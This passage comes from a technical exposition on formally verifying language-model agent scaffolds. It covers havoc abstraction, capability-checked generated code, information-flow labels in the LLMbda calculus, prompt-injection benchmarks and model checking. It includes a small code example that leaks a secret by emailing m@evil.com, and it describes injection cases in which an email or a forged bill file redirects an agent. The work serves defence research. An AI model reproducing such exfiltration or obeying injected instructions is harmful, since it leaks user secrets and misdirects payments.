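An abstraction can also be too narrow because it assumes a structure that the real system doesn't follow. The refund agent expects one request per reply, but many model interfaces allow several. If the real scaffold starts a separate handler for each request, a single reply with two refunds of 60 can cause the same double payment as a late answer. In TraceFix, some deadlocks remained because agents did not follow the modelled steps.

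### Memory, training and opponents that adapt

None of the five conditions concerns what the model remembers, whether its developer retrains it between calls, or whether it plans ahead. An opponent who adapts might seem more dangerous than an arbitrary list of replies, because it could ask for 60, see whether the payment goes through, and then ask for one more than the remaining allowance.

For safety properties, this opponent is no stronger. Describe it as a strategy $\sigma$ that maps the history so far to the next reply:

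$$r_1 = \sigma(h_0), \qquad r_2 = \sigma(h_1), \qquad r_3 = \sigma(h_2),$$

where $h_i$ is the history after $i$ calls. Let the agent run against $\sigma$ and write down the replies, say `Refund(60)`, `Refund(41)` and an error. Now start the agent again from the same state, with an opponent that ignores the history and reads its replies from this list. At the first call both opponents return $r_1$. The scaffold is deterministic, so it does the same thing in both runs and reaches the second call in the same state. There both return $r_2$, and so on. By induction the two runs are identical. If some strategy can break the cap, then some fixed list of three replies can break it, and the proof already covers every list.

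The same argument applies to memory, retraining and correlated replies. A model with memory is a strategy that depends on earlier calls. Retraining replaces one strategy with another partway through, and the result is still a list of replies. If the replies are correlated, because one model produces them all or because several models follow an agreed plan, some lists become more likely, but no new lists become possible.

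Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026) state this reduction as a formal proposition in *PerMIT*, which describes a memory system for agents. The system keeps text from web pages and tools hidden from the main model until a user, or a model standing in for one, confirms the exact wording. The central theorem, proved in Lean for runs of any length, is that every argument reaching a sensitive tool was either typed by the user or confirmed by the user for that tool. In the Lean version, the main model is an arbitrary function of what it has seen and done, but the attacker's outputs and the user's decisions depend only on their position in the sequence, so the third decision, for example, is fixed before the run begins. Real users react to what is on their screen, so the theorem did not obviously apply to them.

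The proposition closes this gap by recording a reactive user's decisions and replaying them from a list. The induction shows that after $t$ steps, both runs are in the same state and the replay has used exactly as many list entries as the user had made decisions. A step that needs no decision preserves both facts because the states match. A step that needs $j$ decisions takes the next $j$ entries, which are the ones the user gave at that point. The same construction works for an adaptive attacker. This part of the argument is on paper and not in Lean, which matters a little because writing the rest in Lean led Jiang and colleagues to correct their specification in three places. PerMIT also has a theorem that compares two runs, where the reduction needs an extra step to show that the same list works for both.

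The replay argument assumed that the scaffold is deterministic. If it draws random numbers and the property must hold in every run, we can treat those numbers as further arbitrary choices, and the argument still works. For a claim about probabilities, the timing of the draws matters. Suppose the shop drops the guard and instead picks one of the three calls at random each morning and inspects that call all day. Against a fixed list with one excessive refund, the inspection has a one in three chance of catching it. An opponent who adapts can learn from the first few complaints which call the shop inspects, then cheat on the other two. If the shop makes a new choice for every complaint, earlier complaints reveal nothing about which call it will inspect next. *Adaptive Online Prediction by Following the Perturbed Leader* establishes a general version of this for a prediction algorithm that adds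 random noise to its choices. Guarantees against a fixed opponent carry over to an adaptive one if the algorithm draws fresh, independent noise at each step, but if it draws the noise only once, at the start, an adaptive opponent may work it out and force large losses.

### When the reply is a program

The refund agent treats a reply as data. Many agents instead ask the model for a program and run it, which lets one reply combine several tools with loops and conditions. Suppose the refund agent does this, with the command `run(r)` after the model call. Replacing the call by `havoc r` is still sound, but the proof now has to deal with `run(r)`, whose effect depends on which program $r$ is. Together, the two commands have the weakest precondition

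$$\forall p.\ wp(p, Q),$$

where $p$ ranges over all programs in the language. If the language is unrestricted, this is false for every $Q$, even $Q = \text{true}$, because $p$ might loop forever. A time limit would stop the loop, but $p$ could also reset `paid` to 0 or contact the bank directly.

Analysing the scaffold in advance does not solve this. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* assumes that a script that can reach `eval` or `exec`, the usual commands for running text as code, may have any effect, so the script cannot get the highest level of certification. Dantas and colleagues describe static analysis as limited to finite workflows laid out beforehand, whereas most realistic agents plan while running.

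The alternative is to check each program when it arrives and run only those in some set $P$ that a checker accepts. The proof then needs $wp(p, Q)$ only for $p$ in $P$. There are still infinitely many such programs, but we don't have to reason about each one. Give the generated program a single way to pay, an operation `refund(x)` that contains the guard, and keep `paid` out of its reach. Whatever the program computes, its effect on payments is then a sequence

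$$\text{refund}(x_1),\ \text{refund}(x_2),\ \ldots,\ \text{refund}(x_k)$$

with amounts and a length that the opponent picks. Each operation preserves `paid <= 100`, so every such sequence does too. In terms of simulation, the abstract system is a loop that repeatedly applies `havoc` to `x` and calls `refund(x)`. It stands still while the generated program does its internal calculations. What remains is to show that accepted programs really have no other way to affect payments.

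One way to ensure this is with capabilities. A capability is a value that a program must hold in order to perform some action. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) used capabilities to build a system called TACIT. The agent submits Scala code, a compiler checks it in a restricted "safe mode", and only code that passes will run. They treat the model itself as a potential attacker. They require that programs cannot forge capabilities, because otherwise a generated program could build its own access to `paid`. They also require that capabilities control every effect relevant to safety, except those that the runtime can contain. If capabilities did not cover the network, for example, the program could go to the payment service without calling `refund`. Finally, they require that the type system can mark a computation as having no side effects, which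 they use to protect confidential data.

Code in safe mode can still throw exceptions, because almost any program can divide by zero or run out of memory. The runtime catches these exceptions and turns them into ordinary failure values. The first condition therefore applies here too, since the scaffold has to handle errors from generated code as well as from the model.

### Generated programs in L3M

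L3M applies the same approach in Lean. An agent that keeps repeating a sequence of steps can write it as a Lean program, which becomes a new tool the next time the agent starts. Before offering the tool to the model, the runtime checks the program in three ways.

The runtime first checks that the program is a single expression without local recursion. It does this before Lean processes the code in full, because processing Lean code can execute code. The runtime also rejects functions marked as unsafe, capabilities created outside their own module, and any axiom beyond Lean's three standard ones. An extra axiom could make anything provable, as `assume false` would.

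Next comes the type. Leaving out some details, an accepted program has the type

$$\text{for every } m \text{ with the listed operations:}\quad \text{capabilities} \to \text{input} \to m(\text{output}).$$

Here $m$ stands for the environment the program runs in. The program must work for every such environment, so it can call only the operations it receives and nothing specific to the real operating system. L3M offers eleven groups of operations, such as reading files or fetching web pages, and each program lists the groups it uses. A program that fetches a web page without listing network access fails type checking.

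The last check compares this list with what the agent is already allowed to do. For example, a network capability contains the names of the permitted hosts, and the program gets the agent's own capability. A new tool therefore cannot give the agent access to anything new.

Eisenach and colleagues acknowledge that they have proved only part of the step from "for all accepted programs" to "no other effects" in L3M. They have Lean theorems about individual checks, including that an accepted program contains no forbidden syntax and that everything it names directly is on the permitted list. They have not proved that the checks together confine every malicious program, and rely on an informal argument and tests for that. To ensure that nobody can forge capabilities, they use a code checker that runs with every build rather than a proof.

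Restricting the agent can also lower its performance. On 37 tasks from a benchmark of command-line work, L3M scored 27.0% when its tools were limited to actions that it could undo or had bounded in advance, and 41.7% when it also had a general-purpose shell. Odersky and colleagues report no significant loss from requiring capability-safe code, so the loss probably depends on how much the permitted operations cover.

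Every proof about a scaffold rests on facts about the outside world. L3M is unusually explicit about some of them. It writes each of these assumptions as a Lean proposition, together with observations that would show it to be false, and any theorem that needs the assumption lists it as a hypothesis. The theorem that L3M can restore an edited file assumes that Git, the version-control program that stores L3M's data, returns the same bytes it stored. The theorem that L3M can undo a commit assumes that Git's reset command restores the earlier state. For tasks that run in containers (isolated environments on a shared machine), L3M assumes that the container software enforces the plan it receives. Other dependencies belong to the trusted base without any such statement. They include Lean itself, the Linux kernel, six small C files and the model provider's interface.

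For the refund agent, the corresponding assumption would be that `pay(x)` transfers exactly `x`, once, and the shop's bank statement could show that this is false. It is hard to guarantee that the transfer happens only once. L3M records each action in a log before starting it, but Eisenach and colleagues note that the action and the record of its result are separate operations. The refund agent has the same gap between `pay(x)` and `paid := paid + x`. If the machine crashes there after a payment of 60 and restarts from the saved value of `paid`, the next `Refund(60)` passes the guard and the customer gets 120. One repair is to save the new total and a unique payment number before calling `pay`. The agent can then repeat the request with the same number after a crash, provided the payment service ignores numbers it has already processed.

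## Which properties survive the replacement, and which are lost?

If the real model call meets the five conditions, every run of the real agent matches a run of the program with `havoc r`. Let $R$ be the set of real runs and $A$ the set of abstract runs, recording only the scaffold's actions in each. Then $R \subseteq A$. Whether a fact about $A$ also holds for $R$ depends on the kind of fact.

### Properties of a single run

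Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, define a trace property as a set $P$ of runs. A system satisfies it if all of the system's runs are in $P$. If the abstract agent satisfies $P$, then

$$R \subseteq A \subseteq P,$$

so the real agent satisfies it too. This covers every safety property of what the scaffold does, such as the refund cap, the limit of three calls, and rules about order. One of Clarkson and Schneider's examples is a rule that a system may not write to the network after reading a file. Liveness properties also concern single runs, but they need further assumptions, because an opponent can usually prevent the wanted event.

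Properties of the model's reply alone are lost unless the reply's type guarantees them. By the `havoc` rule, we can prove such a property only if every value of `r` satisfies it. "The model never outputs a request for more than 100" is false because `r` can be `Refund(5000)`. "The model never outputs a request for a negative amount" is true, but only because the parser rejects such requests before they become values of `r`. "The model never outputs a request that would break the cap" is also false, because the guard blocks the payment only after the model has output the request.

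Some properties of the scaffold's own actions are also lost. The refund agent's `send` action passes `text` to the customer unchanged, so "the agent never insults a customer" fails. The cap survives because the guard restricts `x` before `pay` uses it.

### Claims that something is possible

"The agent can pay a refund" means that some run contains a payment. This is true in $A$, since the opponent may return `Refund(60)`, but it may be false in $R$, since a real model might refuse every request.

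If no run in $A$ contains a payment, then no run in $R$ does either. This gives a useful check on a safety proof, because an agent that never pays satisfies the cap. If a programmer mistypes the guard as `paid + x < 0`, the proof of the cap still succeeds, but a search for a reply that leads to a payment finds none. One recorded payment is enough to show that the real agent can pay.

### Probabilities and quality

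`havoc` assigns no probabilities, so the abstract program cannot show whether fewer than 1% of customers go unanswered. If some list of replies leaves a customer unanswered, the probability of that outcome could be anything from 0 to 1, depending on the model. The program also cannot express that a refund went to someone who deserved it, because none of its variables record this. Probabilities have to come from a particular model. *BEAVER* gives probability bounds for such a model, and *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (Nazeri, Schmuck and colleagues, 2026) gives guaranteed lower bounds on the probability of a harmful reply.

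We know the probabilities of the scaffold's own coin flips, unlike those of the model's outputs. *A Demonic Outcome Logic for Randomized Nondeterminism* (Zilberstein, Kozen and colleagues, 2025) gives proof rules for programs that mix random and demonic choice. In its first example, an opponent tries to match a fair coin. The two agree with probability exactly ½ if the opponent chooses before the flip, but an opponent who chooses after it can make them agree with any probability.

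A scaffold that flips a coin to decide whether a person reviews a refund request has to flip it after the model's reply arrives. If it flips the coin before the call, the proof fails even if the result never appears in the prompt, because `havoc` does not limit what information the opponent can use to choose the reply. Cryptographic protocol analysis has ways to limit this information.

### Secrets and hyperproperties

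Privacy rules need a comparison between runs. Suppose the shop's prompt includes a secret bit $h$, which is 1 if the shop suspects the customer of fraud. To keep the example small, let the reply also be a single bit, which goes to the customer:

```
prompt := complaint + h
havoc r                  # r is 0 or 1
send(r)
```

If $h$ is 1 and the customer receives a 1, we can't tell from this run alone whether anything leaked, because that depends on what the customer would have received if $h$ had been 0. Clarkson and Schneider call this kind of requirement a hyperproperty, which is a set of sets of runs. A system satisfies a hyperproperty if the set of all its runs is one of those sets. An upper limit on the average response time over all runs is another example, because whether one slow run is acceptable depends on the others.

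Take the rule "the replies the customer might receive are the same whatever the secret is". Writing each run as $(h, r)$, the abstract program has four:

$$(0,0),\quad (0,1),\quad (1,0),\quad (1,1).$$

Both replies are possible for both values of $h$, so the program satisfies the rule. Replacing `havoc r` with a model that copies the secret, `r := h`, is a legal refinement because the model always terminates and changes only `r`. Only the runs $(0,0)$ and $(1,1)$ remain, so the customer can read the secret from the reply. The proof about the abstract program was correct, but it does not apply to the program with this model.

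Jeremy Jacob described the problem in 1989, and it later became known as the refinement paradox. *A General Theory of Composition for Trace Sets Closed Under Selective Interleaving* (McLean, 1994) uses a similar echoing system to prove that such a rule cannot be a trace property. Suppose it were, and let $P$ be the set of permitted runs. The system with every possible run satisfies the rule, so $P$ contains every run. Then every system would satisfy the rule, including the one that echoes the secret, but that system violates it.

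Clarkson and Schneider show that refinement preserves exactly the subset-closed hyperproperties. A hyperproperty is subset-closed if, whenever a set of runs satisfies it, every subset does too. The rule about possible replies is not subset-closed, because it requires certain runs to exist. If $(0,0)$ and $(1,1)$ are possible, the rule requires $(0,1)$ and $(1,0)$ to be possible too, but a refinement may remove those last two. For the same reason, refinement may not preserve the claim that a refund is possible.

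A stricter rule, observational determinism, requires any two runs that start with the same public information to look the same to the public. This rule is subset-closed because a violation is a pair of runs that are both present, so removing runs cannot create one. But the abstract program violates it, since $(0,0)$ and $(0,1)$ look different to the customer. So does any program that passes on an arbitrary reply, even if the secret was never in the prompt. With plain `havoc`, therefore, refinement can break the weaker rule, and hardly any useful agent satisfies the stricter one.

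McIver and Morgan (2003) point out that refinement preserves only what its definition was designed to preserve, so there is no real paradox. Ordinary refinement doesn't preserve speed either. One response is to change the definition. Mantel (2001) proposes special refinement operators that preserve information-flow properties, and Morgan (2006), in *The Shadow Knows*, defines an "ignorance-preserving" refinement, under which an implementation may reveal no more than its specification. These suit a programmer who chooses each step of a program's development. A shop that buys access to a model would have to prove that the model is a permitted refinement, and therefore that it doesn't copy secrets from its prompt, which brings back the problem of verifying the model.

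### Letting the reply depend on the prompt

A better repair is to change the abstract program. Replace `havoc r` by `r := f(prompt)`, where $f$ is an arbitrary function that stays the same in the two runs being compared. If $out(f, h)$ is what the customer receives, the property to prove becomes

$$\text{for all } f, h, h': \quad out(f, h) = out(f, h').$$

If the prompt contains $h$, the proof fails, as it should, because $f$ may copy $h$ into its reply. If the prompt does not contain $h$, the two runs build the same prompt, receive the same reply and send the same message. The argument extends to several calls by induction, since equal replies lead to equal next prompts. The real model is one of the functions $f$, so the result applies to it.

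Clarkson and Schneider show how to check such properties with ordinary tools. If violations always involve at most $k$ runs, the hyperproperty reduces to a safety property of $k$ copies of the system running side by side. Here $k$ is 2, and the first copy executes `havoc r`. The second copy reuses `r` if the two prompts match, and otherwise executes its own `havoc`.

For a model that samples its replies, $f$ should return a probability distribution, and comparing only which replies are possible is too weak. Suppose a model copies the secret nine times in ten and reverses it otherwise. All four runs are still possible, but a customer who began with even odds and receives a 1 can be 90% sure that the shop suspects fraud. The stronger requirement is that the customer sees the same distribution whatever the secret is.

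The repair adds the assumption that the reply depends on no secret information except what is in the prompt. Memory of earlier conversations made no difference to the refund cap, but it matters here. If the provider carries information over from a conversation that contained $h$, the reply to a harmless prompt could reveal $h$. The proof therefore has to treat such memory as part of the prompt.

Comparing two copies of every agent is laborious, so a practical system attaches labels to data. It marks $h$ and any prompt built from $h$ as secret, and gives each reply its prompt's label. The check before `send` then rejects any reply marked secret. This is stricter than necessary, because it also rejects replies that reveal nothing about $h$.

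### The LLMbda calculus

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, build this repair into their LLMbda calculus. Its main target is prompt injection, in which the model follows instructions in text that an agent was only supposed to read, such as an email or a web page. In most of their examples, a label is a set that may contain U (untrusted) and S (secret). Combining two values combines their labels, and data may flow to a place only if that place permits everything in the data's label.

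The state of a program is its conversation with the model, which has a label of its own. Four constructs act on it:

| Construct | Effect on the conversation | Effect on labels |
|---|---|---|
| `send e` | Adds the value of `e` as a prompt. | The conversation acquires the labels of `e`. |
| `recv` | Samples a reply given the whole conversation, adds it, parses it as code and runs the code. | The result carries at least the conversation's labels. |
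| `fork e` | Runs `e` on a copy, then restores the original. | The result keeps its labels, and the original conversation gains none. |
| `clear` | Empties the conversation. | Only the labels of the decisions that led to this point remain. |

A program can use `fork` and `clear` to ask the model about untrusted text in a separate, empty conversation. The answer is labeled U, but the text itself never enters the main conversation. A tool can use `assert` to stop the program if a value carries a forbidden label. For example, `assert ["S"] x` accepts public or secret values of `x` but not untrusted ones.

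Labels must also account for decisions based on secrets. Suppose a program tells the model "x = false", then adds "Set x = true" only if a secret bit is true, and finally asks for `x`. If the conversation is marked secret only when the second message is sent, a false bit leaks, because the conversation stays public and the answer "false" reveals the bit. LLMbda therefore stops any program that tries to send anything to a public conversation after a decision based on a secret.

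Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL, an earlier defence that also tracks labels, misses leaks of this kind through variables. Their example works roughly like this:

```
tmp := true;  rich := true
if balance > threshold: tmp := false
if tmp: rich := false
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and is labeled secret. The next line doesn't run, so `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `tmp` stays true and public, `rich` becomes false, and no email goes out. CaMeL raises a variable's label only when an assignment runs, so it never marks `rich` as secret.

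CaMeL builds on Simon Willison's dual-LLM pattern, in which one model plans without seeing untrusted data and another reads that data but cannot use tools. CaMeL's planning model writes code, so the agent can have any control flow, but CaMeL has no comparable soundness theorem. FIDES, another defence, has one, but only for a fixed agent loop, and it does not track secrets through decisions that depend on data. In LLMbda, a program can express the separation between models using `fork` and `clear`. LLMbda's theorem covers every program in the language, including programs that run code written by the model.

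### What the noninterference theorem guarantees

Noninterference means that inputs hidden from an observer do not affect what the observer sees. An observer is defined by the labels it can see. If the observer sees everything except secret values, noninterference guarantees privacy. If it sees only trusted values, noninterference protects against injection, because changes to untrusted inputs cannot affect any value marked as trusted.

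Take two starting states that look the same to the observer. Let $\mu(o)$ and $\nu(o)$ be the probabilities that the program finishes with visible outcome $o$ from the first and the second. If the program always finishes, the theorem guarantees $\mu = \nu$. In general some probability may be missing, because the program can run forever or stop at a failed `assert`. The theorem then guarantees that there is some $\omega$ with

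$$\mu(o) \leq \omega(o), \qquad \nu(o) \leq \omega(o) \quad \text{for every } o, \qquad \sum_o \omega(o) \leq 1.$$

In other words, we could make the two distributions equal by having the program finish more often. Suppose the program outputs "yes" or "no" with probability ½ each when the secret is 0. When the secret is 1, it outputs "yes" with probability ½ and otherwise hangs. The theorem allows this, with $\omega$ equal to the first distribution. It does not allow the program to output "yes" with probability 0.6 and "no" with probability 0.4 when the secret is 1, because $\omega$ would have to give "yes" at least 0.6 and "no" at least 0.5, which add up to more than 1.

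Garby and colleagues first tried comparing the distributions conditional on the program finishing. That test would reject the permitted example, because "yes" then has probability ½ in one case and 1 in the other. Under the definition they adopted, the statistical distance between $\mu$ and $\nu$ is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. In the example, the distance and this average are both ¼.

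The proof uses a second way of running programs, which skips a computation as soon as its label becomes invisible to the observer and returns a dummy value instead. This behaves identically for both starting states, because they differ only in hidden data. It also gives every visible outcome at least as much probability as the real program, since skipping a computation can remove a hang or an error but cannot add one. Its distribution therefore serves as $\omega$. The proof holds for every model and every parser, so it covers all $f$, as the repair requires.

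The theorem allows a program to leak information through whether it finishes. A single run reveals at most one bit this way, but repeated runs can reveal more. In CaMeL, an ordinary Python loop outside the label tracking restarts failed attempts, and an attacker could use it to extract a whole secret one bit at a time. In LLMbda, the retry loop can be part of the program, where labels apply to it. The semantics doesn't model time, so the theorem doesn't cover leaks through response times. The guarantee also requires the program to contain all its data sources and tools, and the developer to label the sources correctly and put checks in the right places.

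Strict labels would make the refund agent useless, because the complaint is untrusted, any amount the model bases on it is also untrusted, and a `pay` that requires trusted amounts would reject them all. LLMbda therefore includes `endorse`, which marks an untrusted value as trusted. If the agent endorses only one of $n$ fixed categories, such as "damaged" or "late", an attacker can influence at most $\log_2 n$ bits. An endorsed account number has no such small limit. Garby and colleagues prove that `endorse` cannot turn secret data into public data, but it does weaken the protection against injection. It has no effect in code that runs because of untrusted data, so an injected program cannot use it to mark itself as trusted.

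### The interpreter and the banking test

Garby and colleagues wrote the interpreter in Lean, and their theorems describe the same program that runs the agents. The interpreter takes an oracle as an argument. The oracle is a function that maps the call number and the conversation to a reply, and once it is fixed, the interpreter is deterministic. A further theorem shows that drawing the oracle's replies at random from the model's distribution and then running the interpreter gives exactly the probabilities used in the noninterference theorem. In live use, the oracle is a network request to a model provider. The proof doesn't cover that code, so the noninterference theorem applies only if the provider's replies depend on the conversation in the way the theorem assumes.

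In one LLMbda example, a user asks an agent to find an email and send its author a reminder about a meeting, but the email contains an injected request to send a cancellation instead. An ordinary tool-calling agent, with the email in its main conversation, sent the cancellation. A second agent wrote its whole plan before reading the email, used a separate conversation to extract the sender's address, and sent the reminder. The theorem guarantees that the injection could not have changed the subject or body, which the email tool requires to be labeled trusted. It does not guarantee this for the recipient's address, which came from the email.

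For a larger test, Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori and ran it on the banking part of AgentDojo, a benchmark for prompt injection. Randori first practises on mock data, where files contain placeholder text and payments do nothing, so it can revise its plan without touching untrusted data. It then writes a final plan, which may contain endorsements, and runs it on the benchmark's bank account.

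The test combined 16 user tasks with 9 attacks, which gives 144 pairs. With three repetitions and three models, there were 1,296 attacked runs, and Randori resisted all but two. For two of the models, Garby and colleagues also ran CaMeL, with and without its policy checks:

| System | Model | Tasks completed without attacks | Attacked runs resisted |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 (75%) | 430 of 432 |
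| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 (65%) | 432 of 432 |
| CaMeL, no policy checks | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 (67%) | 239 of 240 |
| CaMeL, no policy checks | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 (71%) | 378 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policy checks | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 (38%) | 231 of 231 |
| CaMeL, policy checks | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 (38%) | 357 of 357 |

The systems have similar security scores. CaMeL without policy checks resisted the attack in all but five of its 622 completed runs, so planning before reading untrusted data prevents most of the attacks on this benchmark. In 97 of the 144 pairs, the attack needs a tool or file that the plan for the user's task would never use. Only the other 47 pairs really test the labels, and even a perfect score on them gives a 95% confidence interval with a lower bound of 92.4%.

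CaMeL completed roughly half as many tasks with its policy checks on as with them off, while Randori, with its checks on, completed about as many as CaMeL without any. The comparison is not exact, because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, in a slightly weaker form, and may endorse untrusted data. Without endorsement, its completion rate fell from 75% to 62.5% on Qwen3.7-plus, the third model, and from 65% to 54% on MiMo-v2.5. Both rates are still well above CaMeL's 38%, so endorsement does not explain the whole gap, but with only 16 tasks the confidence intervals are around 20 points either way. Many of CaMeL's runs under attack also did not finish.

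Both of Randori's failures came from the same pair of user task and attack, with GPT-5.2. The user asks the agent to pay a bill described in a file, and the attacker replaces the file's contents with a different payment request. The agent has to endorse something from the file to pay the bill, and labels cannot distinguish a genuine bill from a forged one. Without endorsement, the agent could pay neither. A cap like the refund agent's would still limit the loss, because it applies regardless of where the amount came from.

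## How does a model checker search every choice the model could make?

The proof of the refund cap needed an invariant that a person had to think of, but a model checker doesn't need one. It mechanically searches a program's possible states, and if it finds a violation, it prints the run that leads there. (The "model" in the name is the description of the program under test, not a language model.) The search needs a finite number of states and a program that can run by itself. The refund agent can't, because it waits for a reply on every pass.

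### Closing an open program

Harel and Pnueli distinguished closed from open systems in 1985. The state of a closed system completely determines what it can do next, while the behavior of an open system also depends on its environment. Kupferman and Vardi, in *Module Checking*, illustrate the difference with two drink machines. Both boil water and then serve coffee or tea, but the first makes the choice internally and the second lets the customer choose. The two machines have the same tree of possible runs. The refund agent is like the second machine, with the language model in the customer's role.

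To check an open program, we must close it by attaching an environment. If the environment is too narrow, the search can miss errors, and if it is too general, the search takes longer and may report errors that could never happen. *Automatically Closing Open Reactive Programs* (Colby, Godefroid and Jagadeesan, 1998) defines the most general environment as one that supplies any possible value whenever the program takes an input, and accepts any output. This environment never causes the search to miss an error. For the refund agent, attaching it means replacing the model call with `havoc r`.

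A direct implementation would branch once for every possible input, so Colby and colleagues remove the inputs instead. Their algorithm deletes every assignment or test that uses a value from the environment, directly or through other variables. Where a deleted test decided which branch the program took, the closed program chooses arbitrarily, so it can do things the original could not. For example, one of their programs takes a number and reports ten times whether it is even or odd, always with the same answer. The closed version makes a new choice each time, so it can report a mixture.

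The method was developed for telephone-switching software at Lucent. The application studied had about ten families of processes, each with 30,000 to several hundred thousand lines of C. Closing it by hand would have meant simulating much of the rest of the switch.

On the refund agent, this algorithm would keep `calls` and `answered`, since neither ever receives a value from a reply, and delete `paid := paid + x`. Checking the closed agent could still show that it never makes more than three payments, but not that they total at most 100. This fits the theorem of Colby and colleagues, by which the algorithm preserves deadlocks and only those assertion violations that don't depend on values from the environment. To check the cap, we have to keep the amounts and make the set of replies finite in some other way.

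### From strings to a finite alphabet

Inputs that always lead to the same behavior can share a single symbol. Finding these groups of inputs is undecidable in general, but they can be approximated conservatively. Stoller's *Domain Partitioning for Open Reactive Systems* describes an analysis that computes such groups for Java programs.

The refund agent is simple enough that its outputs can be grouped into symbols by hand. The parser reduces every string to `Refund(x)`, `Reply(text)` or an error. All reply texts have the same effect on `calls`, `paid` and `answered`, so they need only one symbol. The guard blocks every request above 100, whatever has been paid so far, so these requests have the same effect as an error. That leaves 101 refund amounts, one symbol for `Reply` and one for everything else. These 103 symbols replace about $10^{2500}$ strings, and the three variables behave exactly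 as before.

Another way is to record only whether certain conditions, called predicates, are true. For the correct agent, two predicates are enough: `paid <= 100` and `paid + x <= 100`, where `x` is the requested amount. The agent pays only when the second is true, which keeps `paid` at 100 or less, so the checker can prove that the agent never exceeds the cap without recording any amounts.

Predicates can also discard too much information. The faulty guard tests only `x <= 100`, so the checker has to consider a request that is at most 100 but does not fit. This can't happen on the first call, because nothing has been paid yet, but the two predicates don't record that, so the checker would falsely report a violation after one reply. Adding the predicate `paid = 0` removes the false alarm but keeps the real violation, which takes two replies.

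A checker may not cover every reply even when the set of actions is finite. *Verifying Memoryless Sequential Decision-making of Large Language Models* (Gross, Spieker and Gotlieb, 2025) describes a tool that parses a model's text into one of a few actions, such as the four directions on a grid, and can use a default action if the text is unusable. The tool queries a particular model, with fixed random seeds, in each reachable state and explores only the action the model chooses. This gives exact probabilities of failure for that model with that prompt, but a new model version would need a new check.

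### Searching backwards from a violation

For example, suppose the shop refunds only 50 or 100 at a time and the agent has the faulty guard `x <= 100`. The opponent can send `Refund(50)`, `Refund(100)`, `Reply` or an error. We distinguish four values of `paid` (0, 50, 100 and "over 100"), four of `calls` and two of `answered`, which gives 4 × 4 × 2 = 32 states.

Let $B_0$ be the set of states in which `paid` is over 100. For any set of states $Y$, let $Pre(Y)$ be the states from which at least one reply leads into $Y$. The checker computes

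$$B_{k+1} = B_k \cup Pre(B_k)$$

until nothing changes. After $k$ rounds, $B_k$ contains every state from which at most $k$ replies can break the cap.

| Round | States added | A reply that leads into the earlier set |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | `paid` over 100 (8 states) | none needed |
| 1 | `paid` is 50 or 100, `calls` is 0, 1 or 2, no answer yet (6 states) | `Refund(100)` |
| 2 | `paid` is 0, `calls` is 0 or 1, no answer yet (2 states) | `Refund(50)` |
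| 3 | none | |

The state with `calls = 2` and `paid = 0` stays out because only one call is left, and a single refund cannot exceed 100. The starting state enters in round 2, so two replies are enough to break the cap. The last column gives the attack:

(0, 0, no) → (1, 50, no) → (2, 150, no).

With the correct guard, round 1 adds no states, because no reply leads from a permitted state to a forbidden one. The starting state is also outside $B_0$, so the cap holds. The states outside the final set always form an invariant, so the checker has found one by itself.

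This search also shows that the guard `calls = 1 and x <= 100` is safe, which the earlier invariant proof failed to do. Round 1 adds the states where `calls` is 0 and `paid` is 50 or 100. Nothing leads to these states because every pass increases `calls`, so the search stops without reaching the starting state. Nobody has to strengthen the invariant.

Searching states takes much less work than trying every list of replies. With the 103 symbols from before, there are about 1.1 million lists of three replies, but together they reach at most 808 states. Many checkers also search forwards from the start, so they skip states the program can never reach. In either direction, the number of states can grow exponentially with the number of variables, since $n$ yes-or-no variables have $2^n$ combinations.

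### When the environment holds back

A real model might never send some of the replies that the most general environment can send. Linear-time properties that hold in that environment still hold without the runs containing those replies because, like the trace properties above, they concern one run at a time. Kupferman and Vardi note that a program therefore satisfies the same linear-time properties whether we treat it as closed or open.

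Branching-time properties also concern what could have happened instead. In the logic CTL, "AG" means "in every state the system can reach" and "EF" means "some continuation eventually reaches". So "AG EF tea" means that tea always remains possible. An ordinary CTL checker accepts this for both drink machines, but it is wrong about the second, which never serves tea if every customer chooses coffee.

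Module checking, which Kupferman and Vardi introduced, determines whether a property holds however the environment restricts its own choices. It starts with the tree of all possible runs. Wherever the environment has a choice, we may cut some of the branches, as long as at least one remains. The property must hold in every resulting tree, including the uncut one. The second machine fails the property that tea always remains possible, because cutting all the tea branches leaves a tree in which tea is impossible. It also fails the opposite property, which is false in the uncut tree.

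For a scaffold, the property might be that at every point, a case can still reach a human. In one design, the scaffold hands a case over only if the model replies `Escalate`. In another, staff can take over before any model call. Ordinary CTL checking accepts both designs. Module checking rejects the first because the model might never reply `Escalate`, and accepts the second if we count the staff as part of the system. If there may be nobody on duty, the staff belong to the environment, and module checking rejects the second design too.

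Module checking can be much more expensive:

| Logic | Ordinary checking | Module checking |
|---|---|---|
| LTL (linear time) | PSPACE-complete | the same |
| CTL | linear time | EXPTIME-complete |
| CTL* (includes both) | PSPACE-complete | 2EXPTIME-complete |

EXPTIME-complete problems need exponential time in the worst case, and 2EXPTIME-complete ones need doubly exponential time. Checking is this hard because the environment's cuts can encode arbitrary information. Kupferman and Vardi's proof adds to each system state an extra state from which the environment can move to "heaven", where a proposition $q$ is true, or to "hell", where $q$ is false. The environment in effect decides whether $q$ is true at that point by cutting off heaven or leaving it open. Deciding whether some environment satisfies a formula is then as hard as deciding whether the formula is satisfiable at all.

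Checking time grows exponentially with the length of the CTL formula but only polynomially with the size of the program. The most commonly used formulas are also easier to check. The journal version of *Module checking* (Kupferman, Vardi and Wolper, 2001) reports that current tools work correctly, or need only small changes, for properties that must hold on all paths and for properties of the form "possibly" and "always possibly". For "possibly", the tool needs only a small change to its backward search. The search starts with the states where the wanted event occurs, then repeatedly adds system states with at least one successor in the set and environment states whose successors are all in the set. The property holds if the starting state ends up in the set.

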